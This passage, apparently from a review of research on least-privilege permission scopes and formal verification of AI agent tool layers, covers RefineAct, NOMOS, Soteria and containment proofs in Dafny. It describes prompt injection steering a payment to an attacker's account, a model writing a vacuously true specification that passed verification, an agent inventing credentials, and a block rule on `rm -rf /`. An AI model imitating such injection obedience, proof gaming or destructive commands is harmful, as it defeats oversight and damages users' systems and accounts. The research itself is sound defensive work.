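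- The rules about risky text can err in both directions. One example in the paper rejects any command containing `rm -rf /`, which would delete everything on a disk. That text also occurs in `rm -rf /tmp/cache`, which only empties a cache, but not in `rm -r -f /`, which requests the same deletion as the original.
- If three attempts at a revision fail, the agent goes ahead with its last proposal anyway, unless the proposal was to declare the task finished. The conditions in the plan are therefore not guards, since a guard would keep refusing.

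The remaining safeguard is a deterministic check that calls follow the order of a plan written by a model, and the agent can get past it by persisting. Even so, it seems to help. Batole and colleagues tested RefineAct on 144 tasks from ToolEmu, a benchmark in which a language model simulates the tools. The share of tasks with a safety failure fell from 77% to 39%, and the average score for completing the task rose from 1.0 to 1.9 on a scale from 0 to 3. Failures fell from 88% to 40% in software development, where dangerous commands have recognisable text, but only from 84% to 48% for smart-home devices and robots.

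The agents proposed 1,081 actions. The verifier approved 51% outright, sent 27% back for revision, asked for the user's confirmation on 21% and rejected ten actions. The agents found an acceptable revision for 68% of the actions it sent back. This suggests that much of the benefit came from prompting agents to take steps they had carelessly skipped, which would also explain why completion improved.

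The size of the effect is uncertain because the paper is inconsistent about which model ran the agent. Its evaluation section lists GPT-4o-mini for both conditions, while its implementation section lists the stronger o1 for the agent under RefineAct. If that agent did run on o1, some of the improvement came from the better model. Both models are also old now, and a current agent would probably skip fewer steps even without RefineAct.

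### Compiling a written policy

*NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) starts from a company's policy document instead of the user's request. Its compiler splits the document into clauses, and a language model maps each clause to a condition and a set of tools. The model must choose the condition from a fixed vocabulary that a person has prepared, which contains 34 conditions across three customer-service domains. The model does this five times, and the compiler keeps only the rules that win a majority. The rest of the compiler is conventional software.

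Each rule blocks certain tools either while a condition holds or until it does. NOMOS calls the second kind "preconditions", but they are guards in the sense used here, since the gate tests them itself. The gate takes its facts only from tool results and the user's own messages, so an agent can't get past it by claiming that the user has agreed.

Before the extracted rules are enforced, the compiler checks whether each one can work. In the retail domain, the policy requires the agent to authenticate the user at the start of the conversation. The model turned this into a rule that blocked every tool until the user was authenticated, including the two tools that perform authentication, so the agent could never have used any tool. Other rules required the user's confirmation before a lookup, or tested an argument that the tool doesn't have. The checks repaired or rejected 29 of 79 candidate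 rules for an airline (37%) and 7 of 53 for the retailer (13%). After duplicates and minority votes were removed, 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules remained. In a separate run without checks, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could not work.

These checks need only the rule, the tools' schemas and two small tables, with no solver or theorem prover. They can't detect a working rule that has the wrong meaning. For example, a telecom policy required agents to check that a bill was overdue before sending a payment request, but the model produced a rule that forbade payment requests while a bill was overdue. To catch such errors, Yu and colleagues replay the rules over recordings of an unrestricted agent and look for rules that block successful work. The payment rule would have blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful runs.

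They tested the gate on τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service tasks with written policies, and scored violations with separate rules that they wrote by hand. Among calls that changed something, violations fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the retailer. If one "yes" from the customer is taken to cover a whole batch of announced changes, the unrestricted agent's rates are 36.8% and 13.6%, and the gate still lowers both considerably. Under the gate, the airline agent made only a third as many changes but completed more tasks, 47.6% instead of 39.2%, though that difference is significant only when the same task has to succeed two to four times. Retail success didn't change significantly.

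The drawback was greater on AgentDojo, a benchmark that hides injected instructions in the data an agent reads. AgentDojo has no written policies, so Yu and colleagues wrote one for each of its four settings.

| Setting | Attacks that succeed, without → with gate | Ordinary tasks completed, without → with gate |
|---|---|---|
| Banking | 46.5% → 0.0% | 79.2% → 70.8% |
| Slack | 70.5% → 0.0% | 90.5% → 14.3% |
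| Travel | 10.0% → 3.6% | 75.0% → 70.0% |
| Workspace | 7.3% → 0.0% | 87.5% → 65.0% |

Most of the rules allow a call only if the user named the recipient, file or web address it would affect. This blocks calls to an attacker's address, but it also blocks legitimate work on anything the agent found by reading, which includes much of the work in Slack.

The same difficulty affects scopes derived from the request itself. Yu and colleagues compared NOMOS with Progent, a system whose model writes rules about tools and arguments for each task. In their rerun of the banking tests, attacks still succeeded against Progent in 5.6% of cases. Three quarters of the successful attacks came from two tasks, one of which was to pay the bill in a named file. That request doesn't include the recipient's account, so no rule derived from it alone could restrict payment to the right one, and Progent allowed a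 payment to an injected account number. NOMOS refused to pay the attacker's account in that task, but also refused the legitimate payment. Whoever derives the scope must either trust the file, which an attacker may have written, or ask the user.

### Errors in both directions

A scope that permits nothing would stop every attack in these tests. Surapani and colleagues therefore argue that a least-privilege mechanism should also be judged on the legitimate calls it refuses and the work it creates for users. They find no agreed criteria for this in the field.

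Noyan (2026), in *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents*, tests a system that grants a permission only if it lies within a fixed ceiling for the user's department, a classifier predicts that the task needs it, and no rule forbids the resulting combination of permissions. The data consists of 600 tasks in an invented company with 15 permissions, and the classifier was trained on 500 of the tasks. Noyan measures "overshoot", the share of test tasks that receive at least one unnecessary permission, and "undershoot", the share that lack at least one necessary permission.

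On the remaining 100 tasks, a small fine-tuned model had an overshoot of 23% and an undershoot of 21%. Claude Haiku 4.5, given six examples, had a higher overshoot (42%) and a lower undershoot (11%). No configuration met both of the conditions Noyan had set in advance for a deployable system: an undershoot below 10% and a precision of at least 0.90, meaning that roughly nine in ten granted permissions are necessary.

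Noyan also compares how much risk each layer removes. Each permission has a weight of 1, 2 or 3 according to its risk, and the baseline is an agent that holds all 15. The department ceiling removes 27.9% of the weighted total, and adding the classifier raises this to 84.4%. This is good evidence that a standing scope for a whole role leaves a lot of risk to remove. But the measure also counts the removal of permissions the task needed, so a system that granted nothing would score 100%. The combined system withheld something necessary in 23% of tasks.

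Some errors occur because the permissions are too broad. `database_read` accounts for 34% of the weighted excess because it covers both harmless and sensitive data. A classifier of this kind could remove the support agent's `read_account` permission for the parcel task, but it couldn't limit `send_mail` to messages about shipping.

Yan, Weng and colleagues (2026) show in *Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?* that it isn't enough to adjust a classifier's threshold, which trades one kind of error for the other. They gave models 120 terminal tasks and asked which files the agent should be able to read, write or execute. Frontier models often both omitted permissions that the task required and granted unnecessary or sensitive ones. More reasoning made each model more consistent in its own kind of error, whether too broad or too tight. Zabolotnii (2026), in *Trust Is Not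 a Score*, takes this as evidence that authority isn't a single quantity that can be turned up or down.

Yan and colleagues got better results by deriving permissions in two steps. The model first simulates the task to find every permission it might need, then reviews each one and removes those it can't justify. This raised success on sensitive tasks by up to 15.8% for models that had allowed too few permissions, and made attacks less successful against every model tested.

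One can also train the agent to use less authority. In *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, Tu and Tu (2026) trained a small model on 1,500 tasks with a penalty for excess authority. On 500 new tasks, the rate of excess-authority errors fell from 4.56% to 0.79%, and safe completion rose from 64% to 98%. They present this training as a complement to permission gates, which seems right, since an attacker can still use a permission that the agent leaves unused.

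All these measurements depend on knowing the correct answer. *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* (2026), which introduced Noyan's data, reviews 20 disagreements between a model's labels and a person's and attributes 10 of them to the person's mistakes. The corrections mostly concerned high-risk permissions.

User burden is harder to measure than the other errors. A system can replace a wrongful refusal with a prompt, but if the user approves the prompt without reading it, the result can be an excess permission. In RefineAct's test, the verifier called for 231 confirmations in 144 tasks, or about 1.6 per task. The test doesn't show how carefully real users would read them, even if that number seems tolerable.

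### Checking a generated scope against the standing one

Since translations go wrong, it makes sense to limit what a wrong one can do. Write S for the set of call sequences that the support agent's standing scope permits, and N for the set that the generated scope permits. The tool layer accepts the generated scope only if N ⊆ S, which is the comparison of state machines from the previous section. Here are some scopes that a model might produce from "Ask shipping to trace this parcel":

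| Generated scope | Refines the standing scope? | Fits the request? |
|---|---|---|
| Read the ticket; send shipping the trace template | Yes | Yes |
| The same, and read the customer's account | Yes | Too wide |
| Read the ticket; send the repair firm the trace template | Yes | No |
| Refuse every call | Yes | No |
| Read the ticket; send the trace template to shipping or a courier | No | Too wide |

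The check catches only the last of these, because the courier isn't on the company's list.

The check still provides a firm bound, because refinement preserves safety properties. A generated scope that passes can't allow mail to an unlisted address or access to another customer's account, however badly the model misread the request and even if an attacker wrote it. But the bound is no tighter than the standing scope. A generated scope that keeps the account lookup and all the mail to the repair firm passes the check but still lets an agent send out the account number through its choice of templates.

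The tool layer can also accept a derived scope that is too wide, and permit a call only when both that scope and the standing scope permit it. Noyan's system does this with the department ceiling. The combined scope always refines the standing scope, and the parcel task can go ahead even if the model has added a courier. But nobody learns that the translation was wrong, and a model that invented a courier may have made other mistakes that the standing scope doesn't catch.

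Scopes may also need to change during a task. According to Yu and colleagues, a recent version of Progent uses an SMT solver to classify each change as a narrowing or an expansion. Progent narrows a policy automatically but needs the user's approval to expand it. This is a sensible use of refinement because the agent may have read an injected instruction before it requests an expansion. If the support agent requested permission to email billing halfway through a task, the supervisor would have to approve it, even though the standing scope allows such emails.

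Parkinson and colleagues propose a way to allow some expansions without a prompt. An agent starts with a small baseline and may borrow permissions within an envelope that its owner has set, which corresponds to the standing scope. Each loan expires and uses up part of a budget. More powerful permissions use more of the budget, for example 1 unit for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administration. The amount also rises as a session comes closer to combining untrusted input, sensitive data and a channel that can send data out or change something. One of these multiplies the amount by 1.5, two multiply it by 3, and the system refuses the third. For the support agent, this would block mail to the repair firm once a session had read both the ticket and the account, much as the "private" state does. The proposal is untested and leaves open whether agents would manage the budget sensibly.

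None of these mechanisms proves that the scope matches the request. A proof would require a third set, M, of the sequences that the supervisor would accept, and the only record of M is an English sentence. *MetaPermit* (2026) notes that the correctness of a generated policy depends on the model's understanding of the task. Batole and colleagues acknowledge that their verifier enforces the specification, not the user's actual goal.

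Generated policies can also look correct but mean something else. *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026) examines policies that a model wrote in Rego, a widely used policy language. In a single attempt, the model got the meaning wrong in 62.5% of cases where the written policy called for a denial. A common error was leaving out the active rule that would deny the request, so the code compiled but prohibited nothing. Another was changing "the assigned nurse" to any nurse.

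A refinement check may miss both faults. Suppose the supervisor adds, "Don't contact the repair firm," and the model starts from the standing scope but omits the prohibition. The derived scope is then identical to the standing scope, so it passes the check, because every scope refines itself.

Someone who knows what the request meant therefore has to check the scope. This is easy enough for the parcel task, because the supervisor can read "this ticket, and one trace request to shipping" in a few seconds and approve it once, before the agent starts. It is harder when the task needs dozens of calls, or when the recipient is unknown until the agent opens a file.

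## Proving that the tool layer stays within the scope

Once the supervisor has approved a scope, the company still has to trust the program that enforces it. The support agent's state machine fits in a few lines, but the tool layer around it must also parse the model's output, keep a record of each session, communicate with a mail server and handle errors. A mistake in any of these could let a forbidden call through. Testing will find some mistakes, but nobody can test every call a model might propose.

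Moon and Varshney replace part of this testing with a proof. Their method, containment verification, uses refinement to prove that the software around a model never produces an effect that a stated policy forbids. As far as they know, nobody had verified an agent framework this way before.

### Letting the model output anything

The layer's behavior depends on what the model proposes, so the proof must include an assumption about the model. Moon and Varshney assume only that it returns some value of the type `Action`, which lists the calls the layer supports. They write the proof in Dafny, a programming language whose verifier checks a program's stated guarantees before the program runs. They represent the model as a method without a body. The verifier has no information about which value this method returns, so it accepts a guarantee about the layer only if the guarantee holds for every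 possible value. Verification tools have long used this technique, known as havoc, for unpredictable inputs.

Every real model satisfies this assumption. Careless models, models under prompt injection and models trying to escape all produce some sequence of actions, and the proof covers all sequences. It also covers models with random outputs, because each run still produces a single sequence.

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* mentions the alternative of making assumptions about how likely the model is to produce each output and proving what happens in the expected case. The paper doesn't pursue it. An attacker who can put text in front of the model can change those probabilities, so such a guarantee would be much weaker against prompt injection.

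### Matching the code to the specification

Moon and Varshney describe both the specification and the code as labelled transition systems, which consist of states and the steps between them:

```
s --a/e--> s'     in state s, the model proposes action a;
                  event e occurs, and the new state is s'
```

The event is what happens outside the layer, such as a mail going out. Every state needs at least one step for every action, so the layer always responds. A refusal is a step whose event has no outside effect. A policy Π(s, a, e, s′) determines whether a single step is allowed. For the support agent, part of Π would require that if e is a mail, then the session is open, the recipient is in A and the template is in T.

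The specification M can be the support agent's state machine. The implementation I describes the code, whose states contain more detail, such as a flag `opened` and a log. Whoever writes the proof has to supply two relations between M and I. R relates states. It pairs "new" with every code state in which `opened` is false, and "open" with every code state in which it is true, as long as the ticket, customer and lists agree. Q relates events. It pairs a mail in the specification with a message that leaves the server for the same address with the same template, and a refusal with an error message to the model.

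The code refines the specification if three conditions hold:

```
initial states        R relates the two starting states

step simulation       if R relates s_M and s_I, then for every step of the code
                          s_I --a/e_I--> s_I'
                      the specification has a step with the same action
                          s_M --a/e_M--> s_M'
                      such that R relates s_M' and s_I', and Q relates e_M and e_I

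policy preservation   for every such pair of steps,
                          Π_M(s_M, a, e_M, s_M')  implies  Π_I(s_I, a, e_I, s_I')
```

In the support agent's code, a fresh session has `opened` set to false, which R relates to "new", so the condition on initial states holds.

Suppose the agent has read its ticket and proposes send_mail(shipping, trace). The code finds shipping on its list, sends the message and adds a line to its log. The specification has a step with the same action and the same mail, which leaves the session "open". R does not depend on the log, so it still relates the two states. The policy permits the mail in the specification, so it also permits the real message, which has the same address and template.

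If the agent proposes send_mail(courier, trace), the code doesn't find the courier on its list, so it returns an error message and leaves the session unchanged. The specification also rejects the call and stays in the same state, so the steps match. Neither step sends mail, so neither violates the policy.

Suppose the code has a bug where it splits the recipient field at commas but checks only the first address. Given "shipping, courier", it sends two messages. The full text isn't one of the four addresses, so the specification allows only a refusal, and Q doesn't relate a refusal to outgoing mail. Step simulation therefore fails, and Dafny rejects the proof. This catches the bug even if nobody thought of commas in advance, because the proof has to cover every text that the model could put in the field.

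A badly chosen Q could hide this bug by relating refusals to outgoing mail. Policy preservation guards against this because the specification's refusal satisfies Π_M but the mail to the courier violates Π_I, so the implication from Π_M to Π_I is false.

### Why every run is safe

The soundness theorem also assumes that every step of the specification satisfies Π_M, no matter which actions the model proposes. This needs a separate proof, which is usually easy because the specification is small. The theorem then states that every step of the code satisfies Π_I, again for any proposed actions.

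The proof is by induction on the steps of a run. In any run of the code, whichever model chooses the actions, R relates the starting states of the code and the specification. If R relates the states reached after some number of steps, step simulation gives a step of the specification with the same action as the code's next step, and R relates the resulting states too. The specification therefore has a complete run with exactly the actions that the model chose. Every step of that run satisfies Π_M, because the assumption covers all sequences of actions. By policy preservation, each step of the code then satisfies Π_I.

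This argument does not depend on why the model chose an action, so a company could replace the model with a far more capable one without redoing the proof. This is the method's main attraction, since evidence about a model's good behaviour may not carry over to its successor. The guarantee does assume effect exclusivity, which means that the agent can affect the outside world only through the verified layer.

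### The proof for PocketFlow

Moon and Varshney applied the method to PocketFlow, an agent framework of about 100 lines. A PocketFlow program is a graph whose nodes perform steps of a workflow. After each node runs, a dispatch loop follows the edge whose label matches the node's output. Larger frameworks such as LangGraph contain a similar loop.

The verified version accepts four types of action and enforces three policies: the agent may read files only under a chosen workspace folder, may call only listed tools, and must stop after a set number of steps. The theorem covers every sequence of the four action types. Dafny compiles the verified code to Python. Moon and Varshney also tested the compiled code with a mix of permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only permitted events.

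Language models wrote most of the formal material. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote specifications and proofs, which it revised when Dafny rejected them. The process ran four times on two workflows, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions. Dafny eventually accepted every proof, and took 1.2 to 2.5 seconds to check each path through a workflow. Each run used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens, which costs little compared with the expert labour that such proofs used to require.

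PocketFlow is a very small target. Moon and Varshney leave open whether the process would work for a framework with dozens of action types and more complicated dispatch. The theorem itself would carry over, but someone would have to prove more cases.

### Policies that are true of nothing

A model that writes both a specification and its proof could make the task easy by choosing a specification that demands nothing. Moon and Varshney therefore put up an "information barrier": the step that writes the policy receives the interface and a template of properties, but not the code, so it can't simply describe what the code already does. Each specification then has to pass three tests:

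- Resolution: Dafny must be able to parse and type-check it within thirty seconds.
- Vacuity: the test removes nearly all the content of the proof, and Dafny must reject what remains. If it accepts an empty proof, the specification demanded too little.
- Discrimination: a model inserts a plausible mistake into the proof, and Dafny must reject the result.

All four runs passed all three tests, but one kind of specification still failed to protect anything. The document workflow kept a list of allowed documents and recorded the ones it had read in a field called `docs_read`. Instead of this field, the template had `tool_calls` and `allowed_tools`, with a policy that every recorded tool call must be on the list of allowed tools.

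With the barrier in place, the model treated each document as a tool call. The names were odd, but the resulting proof did show that the workflow reads only allowed documents. Without the barrier, the model could see that `docs_read` had no counterpart in the template, and it wrote a specification in which `tool_calls` never changes. The policy then became:

```
for every j < |tool_calls|:   tool_calls[j] ∈ allowed_tools       where |tool_calls| = 0
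```

This is vacuously true because the list is always empty. Dafny accepted the proof, which placed no restriction on documents.

The tests missed this because they damage the proof as a whole. Much of that proof concerns bookkeeping, such as showing that the recorded history is as long as the number of steps taken, so Dafny rejects the damaged proof even when one of the policies is empty. Moon and Varshney propose also checking that each policy applies to something in at least one reachable state. For the support agent, this would mean showing a run in which an email is sent. The check seems worth doing for every policy, including those written by people, who also make this mistake.

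A policy can also apply to real events and still be too weak. In the PocketFlow theorem, the workspace policy requires every recorded path to start with the workspace folder. If the check compares plain text, `/work/../payroll` passes for the folder `/work`, even though the two dots lead back out of it. The layer would have to resolve such paths before checking them.

A specification can be valid in form and wrong in meaning. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) reviews 38 studies on specifying, verifying and enforcing safe behaviour in agents, and describes specification as the bottleneck. It cites a benchmark in which GPT-4o translated English into a formal planning language. The output was valid 96.1% of the time but had the right meaning only 24.8% of the time. The best fine-tuned model got the meaning right 34.2% of the time. Newer models presumably do better.

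### A layer that refuses every call

A tool layer can satisfy trace inclusion and still be useless. The University of Oxford's *CSP Refinement*, part of the manual for the refinement checker FDR, gives the extreme case. In CSP, a notation for communicating processes, the process STOP never does anything, yet it satisfies every safety specification.

Moon and Varshney's conditions exclude a layer that never responds, but depending on the specification, they may admit one that answers every call with an error. If the specification always sends a permitted mail, this layer fails step simulation because its refusal has no matching step. In practice, a specification usually has to allow refusals when the mail server is down or too busy. If it allows them at any time, the layer passes.

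CSP addresses this with a stricter comparison called failures refinement. A *failure* is a pair (s, X), where s is a trace and X is a set of events that the process can refuse after s. Every failure of the implementation must also be a failure of the specification. If the support agent's specification never allows the layer to refuse mail to shipping once the agent has read its ticket, a layer that refuses such mail at that point has a failure that the specification lacks, and the check rejects the layer. FDR can also check for *divergence*, in which a process works internally forever without responding, as when a layer endlessly retries a broken connection.

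*On the limits of refinement-testing for model-checking CSP* proves that refinement checks can express every safety property, but not certain important properties that require something good to eventually happen. These include properties that rely on fairness assumptions. One example is that an email eventually goes out, provided that the server doesn't stay down forever.

When permissions have usage limits, widening one can break a task that used to work. *Agenra* gives an example in which the first permission allows one deletion of file B and the second allows one deletion of file A. The monitor counts each call against the first permission that fits, so an agent can delete A and then B. Suppose an administrator extends the first permission to cover either file. Deleting A now uses up the first permission, and the second covers only A, so the agent can no longer delete B. It can also delete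 A twice, which the old policy did not allow.

*Agenra* therefore checks separately whether a policy is safe and whether a revision preserves every workflow that the old policy allowed. For the second check, Lean verifies that the new permissions allow every call the old ones would allow, after any number of earlier calls. In a test on 51 revisions, the checks approved all 21 that preserved the workflows and none of the 30 that broke one. Preserving workflows isn't enough by itself either. When the developers of a report-sending application raise its limit from one email to two, every old workflow survives, but the agent can now send the report twice.

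Even if the tool layer permits everything a task needs, the agent may fail to complete the task. *The Verifier Tax* (2026) tested a safety architecture on simulated customer-service tasks. According to Dantas and colleagues, the architecture blocked up to 94% of unsafe actions, but in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly. After a refusal, the agents tended to look for another forbidden route instead of a permitted one. The study covered only two fairly small open models, and Dantas and colleagues give this finding from a single study their lowest rating for certainty. Stronger agents probably recover better from refusals, but the size of the improvement has to be tested.

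### Verifying the plan instead

Checking an agent's whole plan before it starts might reduce the effort it wastes on forbidden calls. In *Return of the Theorem*, Meijer (2026) argues that no plan should run until automatic solvers have proved that it follows formal business rules. *SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) builds and tests a system of this kind.

Soteria's rules come from a company's policy documents. A language model drafts them, and a person then checks them clause by clause, which took a few hours for each of three benchmarks. For each task, a model writes a plan as a graph. Its nodes are stages of the work, and its edges are tool calls with conditions attached. Dafny then has to prove three things about the plan. In the notation below, Σ(s) describes everything that can be true of the plan's variables on reaching stage s, g is the condition on a branch, and P is the precondition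 of the tool that the branch calls with arguments v:

```
tool contracts       Σ(s) ∧ g  ⇒  P(v)               for every tool call

progress             Σ(s) can be true, and
                     Σ(s)  ⇒  g₁ ∨ … ∨ gₙ            at every unfinished stage s

policy compliance    every rule holds for the log of calls, however the plan ends
```

The proof of progress shows that the plan can reach every stage and can always continue from there. The proof of policy compliance uses an imaginary log of the calls made so far, with their order, arguments and results, and a record of which results each variable came from.

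For example, an airline cancels a reservation only if an agent has confirmed that the passenger hasn't yet flown any part of it. One plan looks up the reservation and cancels it if the customer booked at most 24 hours ago, but never checks for completed flights. On the path that ends in a cancellation, the log contains a call to the cancellation tool but none to the tool that makes this check, so the proof fails. Soteria reports the broken rule to the model, which tries again, up to eight times in the main tests.

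RefineAct also had a model write a plan, but nobody proved that the plan met the request. Here Dafny proves that the plan meets the rules. Using preconditions is legitimate here because the plan acts as the calling code and Dafny checks that it satisfies them.

The proof covers only the plan, and the agent may depart from it. If no plan passes within the allowed attempts, Soteria uses the best partly verified one. A runtime monitor therefore checks every call against the preconditions and rules, which then act as guards. When the monitor blocks a call, the agent can consult the rest of the plan for another way to continue.

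He and colleagues tested Soteria on 207 tasks with four models and recorded no violations. These are the results for Claude Opus 4.6, the strongest of the four:

| Benchmark | Tasks | Completed, no guardrail | Completed without violations, no guardrail | Completed without violations, Soteria |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Airline service | 50 | 64.0% | 52.0% | 88.0% |
| Retail service | 114 | 53.5% | 46.5% | 90.4% |
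| Files, terminal and documents | 43 | 30.2% | 11.6% | 18.6% |

Much of the improvement in retail came from Opus attempting required changes more often. Without a plan, it often gathered all the information it needed and then transferred the customer to a human. It attempted the change in only 57% of the tasks that required one, but with Soteria it always did. On file tasks, Soteria increased the number of safe completions but reduced the total number of completions.

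The monitor blocks calls using the same rules that define a violation, so the absence of violations is less impressive than it looks. He and colleagues also corrected and added rules while auditing the results. The rules still may not capture what the airline wants. In one task, an agent without guardrails upgraded a reservation to business class to make it qualify for cancellation. Soteria's two cancellation rules would allow this if the agent looked up the reservation again after the upgrade and no flights had taken place.

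It is also unclear how much the proofs contributed. He and colleagues added Soteria's parts one at a time on the airline tasks:

| Configuration | Violations, GPT-5.4-mini | Violations, Gemini 3 Flash | Safe completions, GPT-5.4-mini | Safe completions, Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plan without proof | 13 | 27 | 44% | 32% |
| With proof | 10 | 24 | 46% | 32% |
| With proof and reusable sub-plans | 12 | 22 | 50% | 38% |
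| With proof, sub-plans and monitor | 0 | 0 | 60% | 62% |

The monitor had a large effect on both measures, while proving the plan had little effect on either. The comparison did not include a version with the monitor and an unproved plan, which might have done nearly as well. In five runs with GPT-5.4-mini and only three planning attempts, Soteria safely completed 50.8% of tasks on average. AgentSpec, an earlier monitor without verified plans, safely completed 48.0%, and the confidence intervals overlap.

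### Choosing what to prove

A proof about the tool layer covers every plan and every model, so the company needs to repeat it only when the layer or the policy changes. Plans must be verified for each task. In a conversation, Soteria makes a new plan at every turn, which raised the cost of an airline task with Opus from about $0.32 to $0.80. On the single-request file tasks, however, better guidance cut the cost from $0.97 to $0.43. Plans also have to be free of loops, and the proof assumes that every outside tool behaves as its contract describes.

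In return, a verified plan can include obligations about future actions. One of Soteria's rules requires an agent to read a file back after writing it. By Ray's result, a monitor that only blocks calls can't enforce this rule, but Dafny can reject a plan that omits the reading step. Checking the plan can also reveal, before execution starts, that the agent would get stuck halfway, after cancelling something. Dantas and colleagues describe the same trade-off across the field, where checks before execution can cover whole plans but need a finite plan in advance, while runtime checks can handle improvised actions but not the actions still to come.

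The two approaches work well together. Soteria has a strict mode in which the agent may make only the calls that the verified plan allows at the current stage, so the plan serves as a narrow scope for that one task. However, this mode would block an agent that stopped to answer a customer's harmless question about a second reservation. It also relies on the software that compares calls with the plan. Dafny checks Soteria's plans but not this software, so an error there could still let a forbidden call through. A containment proof is well suited to verifying this software.

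If a company can verify only the tool layer or the plan, it should probably verify the layer, because a correct layer with a good policy prevents forbidden harm even if the plan is unsafe. Even a perfect plan can't guarantee this, because the agent may ignore it. The evidence that plans improve completion rates supports giving the agent a plan, though not necessarily a proved one.

### Narrow and wide actions

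The containment theorem covers policies that can be checked at each step from the action, its arguments, the resulting event and the layer's state. These policies include the main safety properties in a permission scope, such as "no mail to an unlisted address", "read the ticket before the account" and, if the state includes a counter, "at most five mails per session". The theorem doesn't cover whether a message is truthful or persuasive, because that depends on what the text means. It also doesn't cover leaks of secrets, because a leak may be visible only when several runs are compared.

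Even a policy on actions and arguments has to connect them to the right facts. In *The Verifier Tax*, a customer wanted to change a delivery address but was reluctant to give personal details. The agent called the customer lookup tool with an invented name and postcode, "John Doe" and 12345, and the tool gave it access to an account. A policy that allowed any well-formed name and postcode would permit this call, and a proof that the tool layer follows that policy would still be correct. The support agent's scope avoids this problem by taking the customer number from the company's own records.

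The guarantee is weakest when a single action can do almost anything. Suppose the company gives the support agent a tool called `run_code`, which runs any program. The specification now has a step in which the model proposes a program, and the resulting event is that the program ran. The containment proof still works, but the program can open a network connection and mail the courier. The company could add a policy that forbids programs which send mail, but no algorithm can decide for every program whether it will do so. Moon and Varshney write that a general shell "collapses the guarantee onto the primitive", meaning that the theorem establishes only that the agent runs code through `run_code` and not by any other means.

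They therefore want developers to expose a small set of specific actions. This suits a support agent, which needs three tools, much better than a coding agent, which often needs a shell. For a coding agent, the company has to confine the programs the agent runs, for example in a sandbox that limits which files and network addresses they can use. The agent's real scope is then whatever the sandbox allows, so a useful proof would have to cover the sandbox too.

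## Choosing a refinement relation that preserves secrecy

A containment proof can show that the support agent's mail reaches only the four listed addresses, but it does not show whether that mail reveals a customer's account number. Ordinary refinement can turn a design that keeps the number secret into one that reveals it.

Suppose the company's mail component puts a one-digit reference on every message, and its specification allows any digit from 0 to 9. The programmer uses the last digit of the customer's account number. The specification allows every message this code sends, so the code is a correct refinement and satisfies every safety property that the specification satisfies. But it also reveals the last digit of the account number to the repair firm.

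Classical refinement does not always preserve secrecy, a problem known as the refinement paradox. *How to brew-up a refinement ordering* (Morgan, 2009) gives a short example. If a secret can have two values, classical refinement allows a developer to replace it with one that can have only a single value, so it is no longer secret.

### Why removing traces can reveal a secret

Describe each run of the mail component by a pair, the last digit of the account number and the reference:

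```
specification    all 100 pairs
code             (0,0)  (1,1)  (2,2)  (3,3)  ...  (9,9)
```

Under the specification, an observer who sees the reference 7 cannot tell which of ten possible account digits is the real one, because ten runs, one for each digit, look the same from outside. The code removes nine of these runs, so the reference reveals the digit. Removing runs preserves safety properties, but ordinary refinement can break secrecy because it may remove the runs that kept the observer from knowing the digit.

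The usual reference for this problem is Jeremy Jacob's 1989 paper *On the Derivation of Secure Components*. Mantel's *Preserving Information Flow Properties under Refinement* (2001) draws two difficulties from it. First, removing behaviour has no predictable effect on secrecy. If the programmer had set every reference to 0, that would also have removed most of the runs, but without harming secrecy. Second, different observers' requirements can conflict, so a developer who secures the system against the repair firm and then against the billing department may undo the earlier work.

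Jacob's own procedure was to refine a system until it was ready to implement, then delete traces for one observer after another until it was secure. Mantel objects that this may never finish, and may not leave a useful system if it does. By the time the deletions begin, the developers have also made all their design decisions without regard to secrecy. Kammüller (2024), in *Security Engineering in IIIf, Part II*, still calls the refinement of information-flow security "an old difficult task".

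### An ordering rule that reveals an event

This kind of leak can occur even if no one copies a secret into a message. Mantel shows this with a system of three events, each of which may happen at most once, in any order. For the support agent, let a be a mail to shipping, b a mail to billing, and s a confidential alert to the fraud team. An observer sees a and b but not s. There are 16 possible traces, including the empty one, and whatever mails the observer sees, the alert may or may not have gone out.

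A developer now decides that billing should get mail only after shipping or the fraud team has heard about the case. This removes the five traces that begin with b:

```
kept       (empty)  a  s  ab  as  sa  sb  abs  asb  sab  sba
removed    b  ba  bs  bas  bsa
```

If the observer sees the mail to billing first, only sb and sba remain possible. The observer can then deduce that there has been a fraud alert, even though the rule seemed to be only about the order of some mails.

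The original system satisfied the *perfect security property*, which has two parts. First, deleting the secret events from any possible trace must give another possible trace, so that the observer can't deduce that a secret event happened. Second, wherever a secret event is possible, every visible continuation that was possible without it must still be possible after it, so that the observer can't deduce that the event didn't happen. The new system fails the first part because it allows the trace sb but not b.

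### Restricting what developers may do

One remedy, which Roscoe, Woodcock and Wulf proposed in 1994, is to make the system's behaviour towards the observer completely deterministic, so that refinement has no visible choice to remove. If the specification fixes every reference at 0, no programmer can hide anything in a reference. Ordinary refinement then preserves secrecy without further proof. But Mantel points out that a specification can no longer leave visible details open for later, and that the rule forbids common forms of parallelism. For example, the company couldn't leave open which of two simultaneous sessions sends its mail first.

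Mantel's own remedy permits visible choices but controls how developers remove them. It relies on a proof about single steps instead of whole traces. The developer groups states that the observer shouldn't be able to tell apart, and proves two conditions:

- A secret event always leads to a state in the same group.
- States in the same group allow the same visible events, which again lead to states in a common group.

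In the example, a state records which of the three events have happened. The eight states form four pairs, and the states in each pair differ only in whether s has happened. The developer's rule blocks b when no event has happened but allows it when only s has happened. These two states form a pair, so the second condition fails.

Mantel provides two operators that repair such a change automatically. The developer lists the events to disable in each state, and one operator disables all of them, plus any others needed to keep the groups matched. Here it also blocks b when only s has happened, so billing can get mail only after shipping has. Nine traces remain, and none reveals the alert.

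The other operator disables only actions the developer listed, and sometimes not all of them. The developer had listed b at the start, along with a and s in the state after an opening b, since that state was supposed to become unreachable. The operator keeps the opening b and the a that may follow it, and disables only the s, so a fraud alert can't go out between an opening mail to billing and the mail to shipping.

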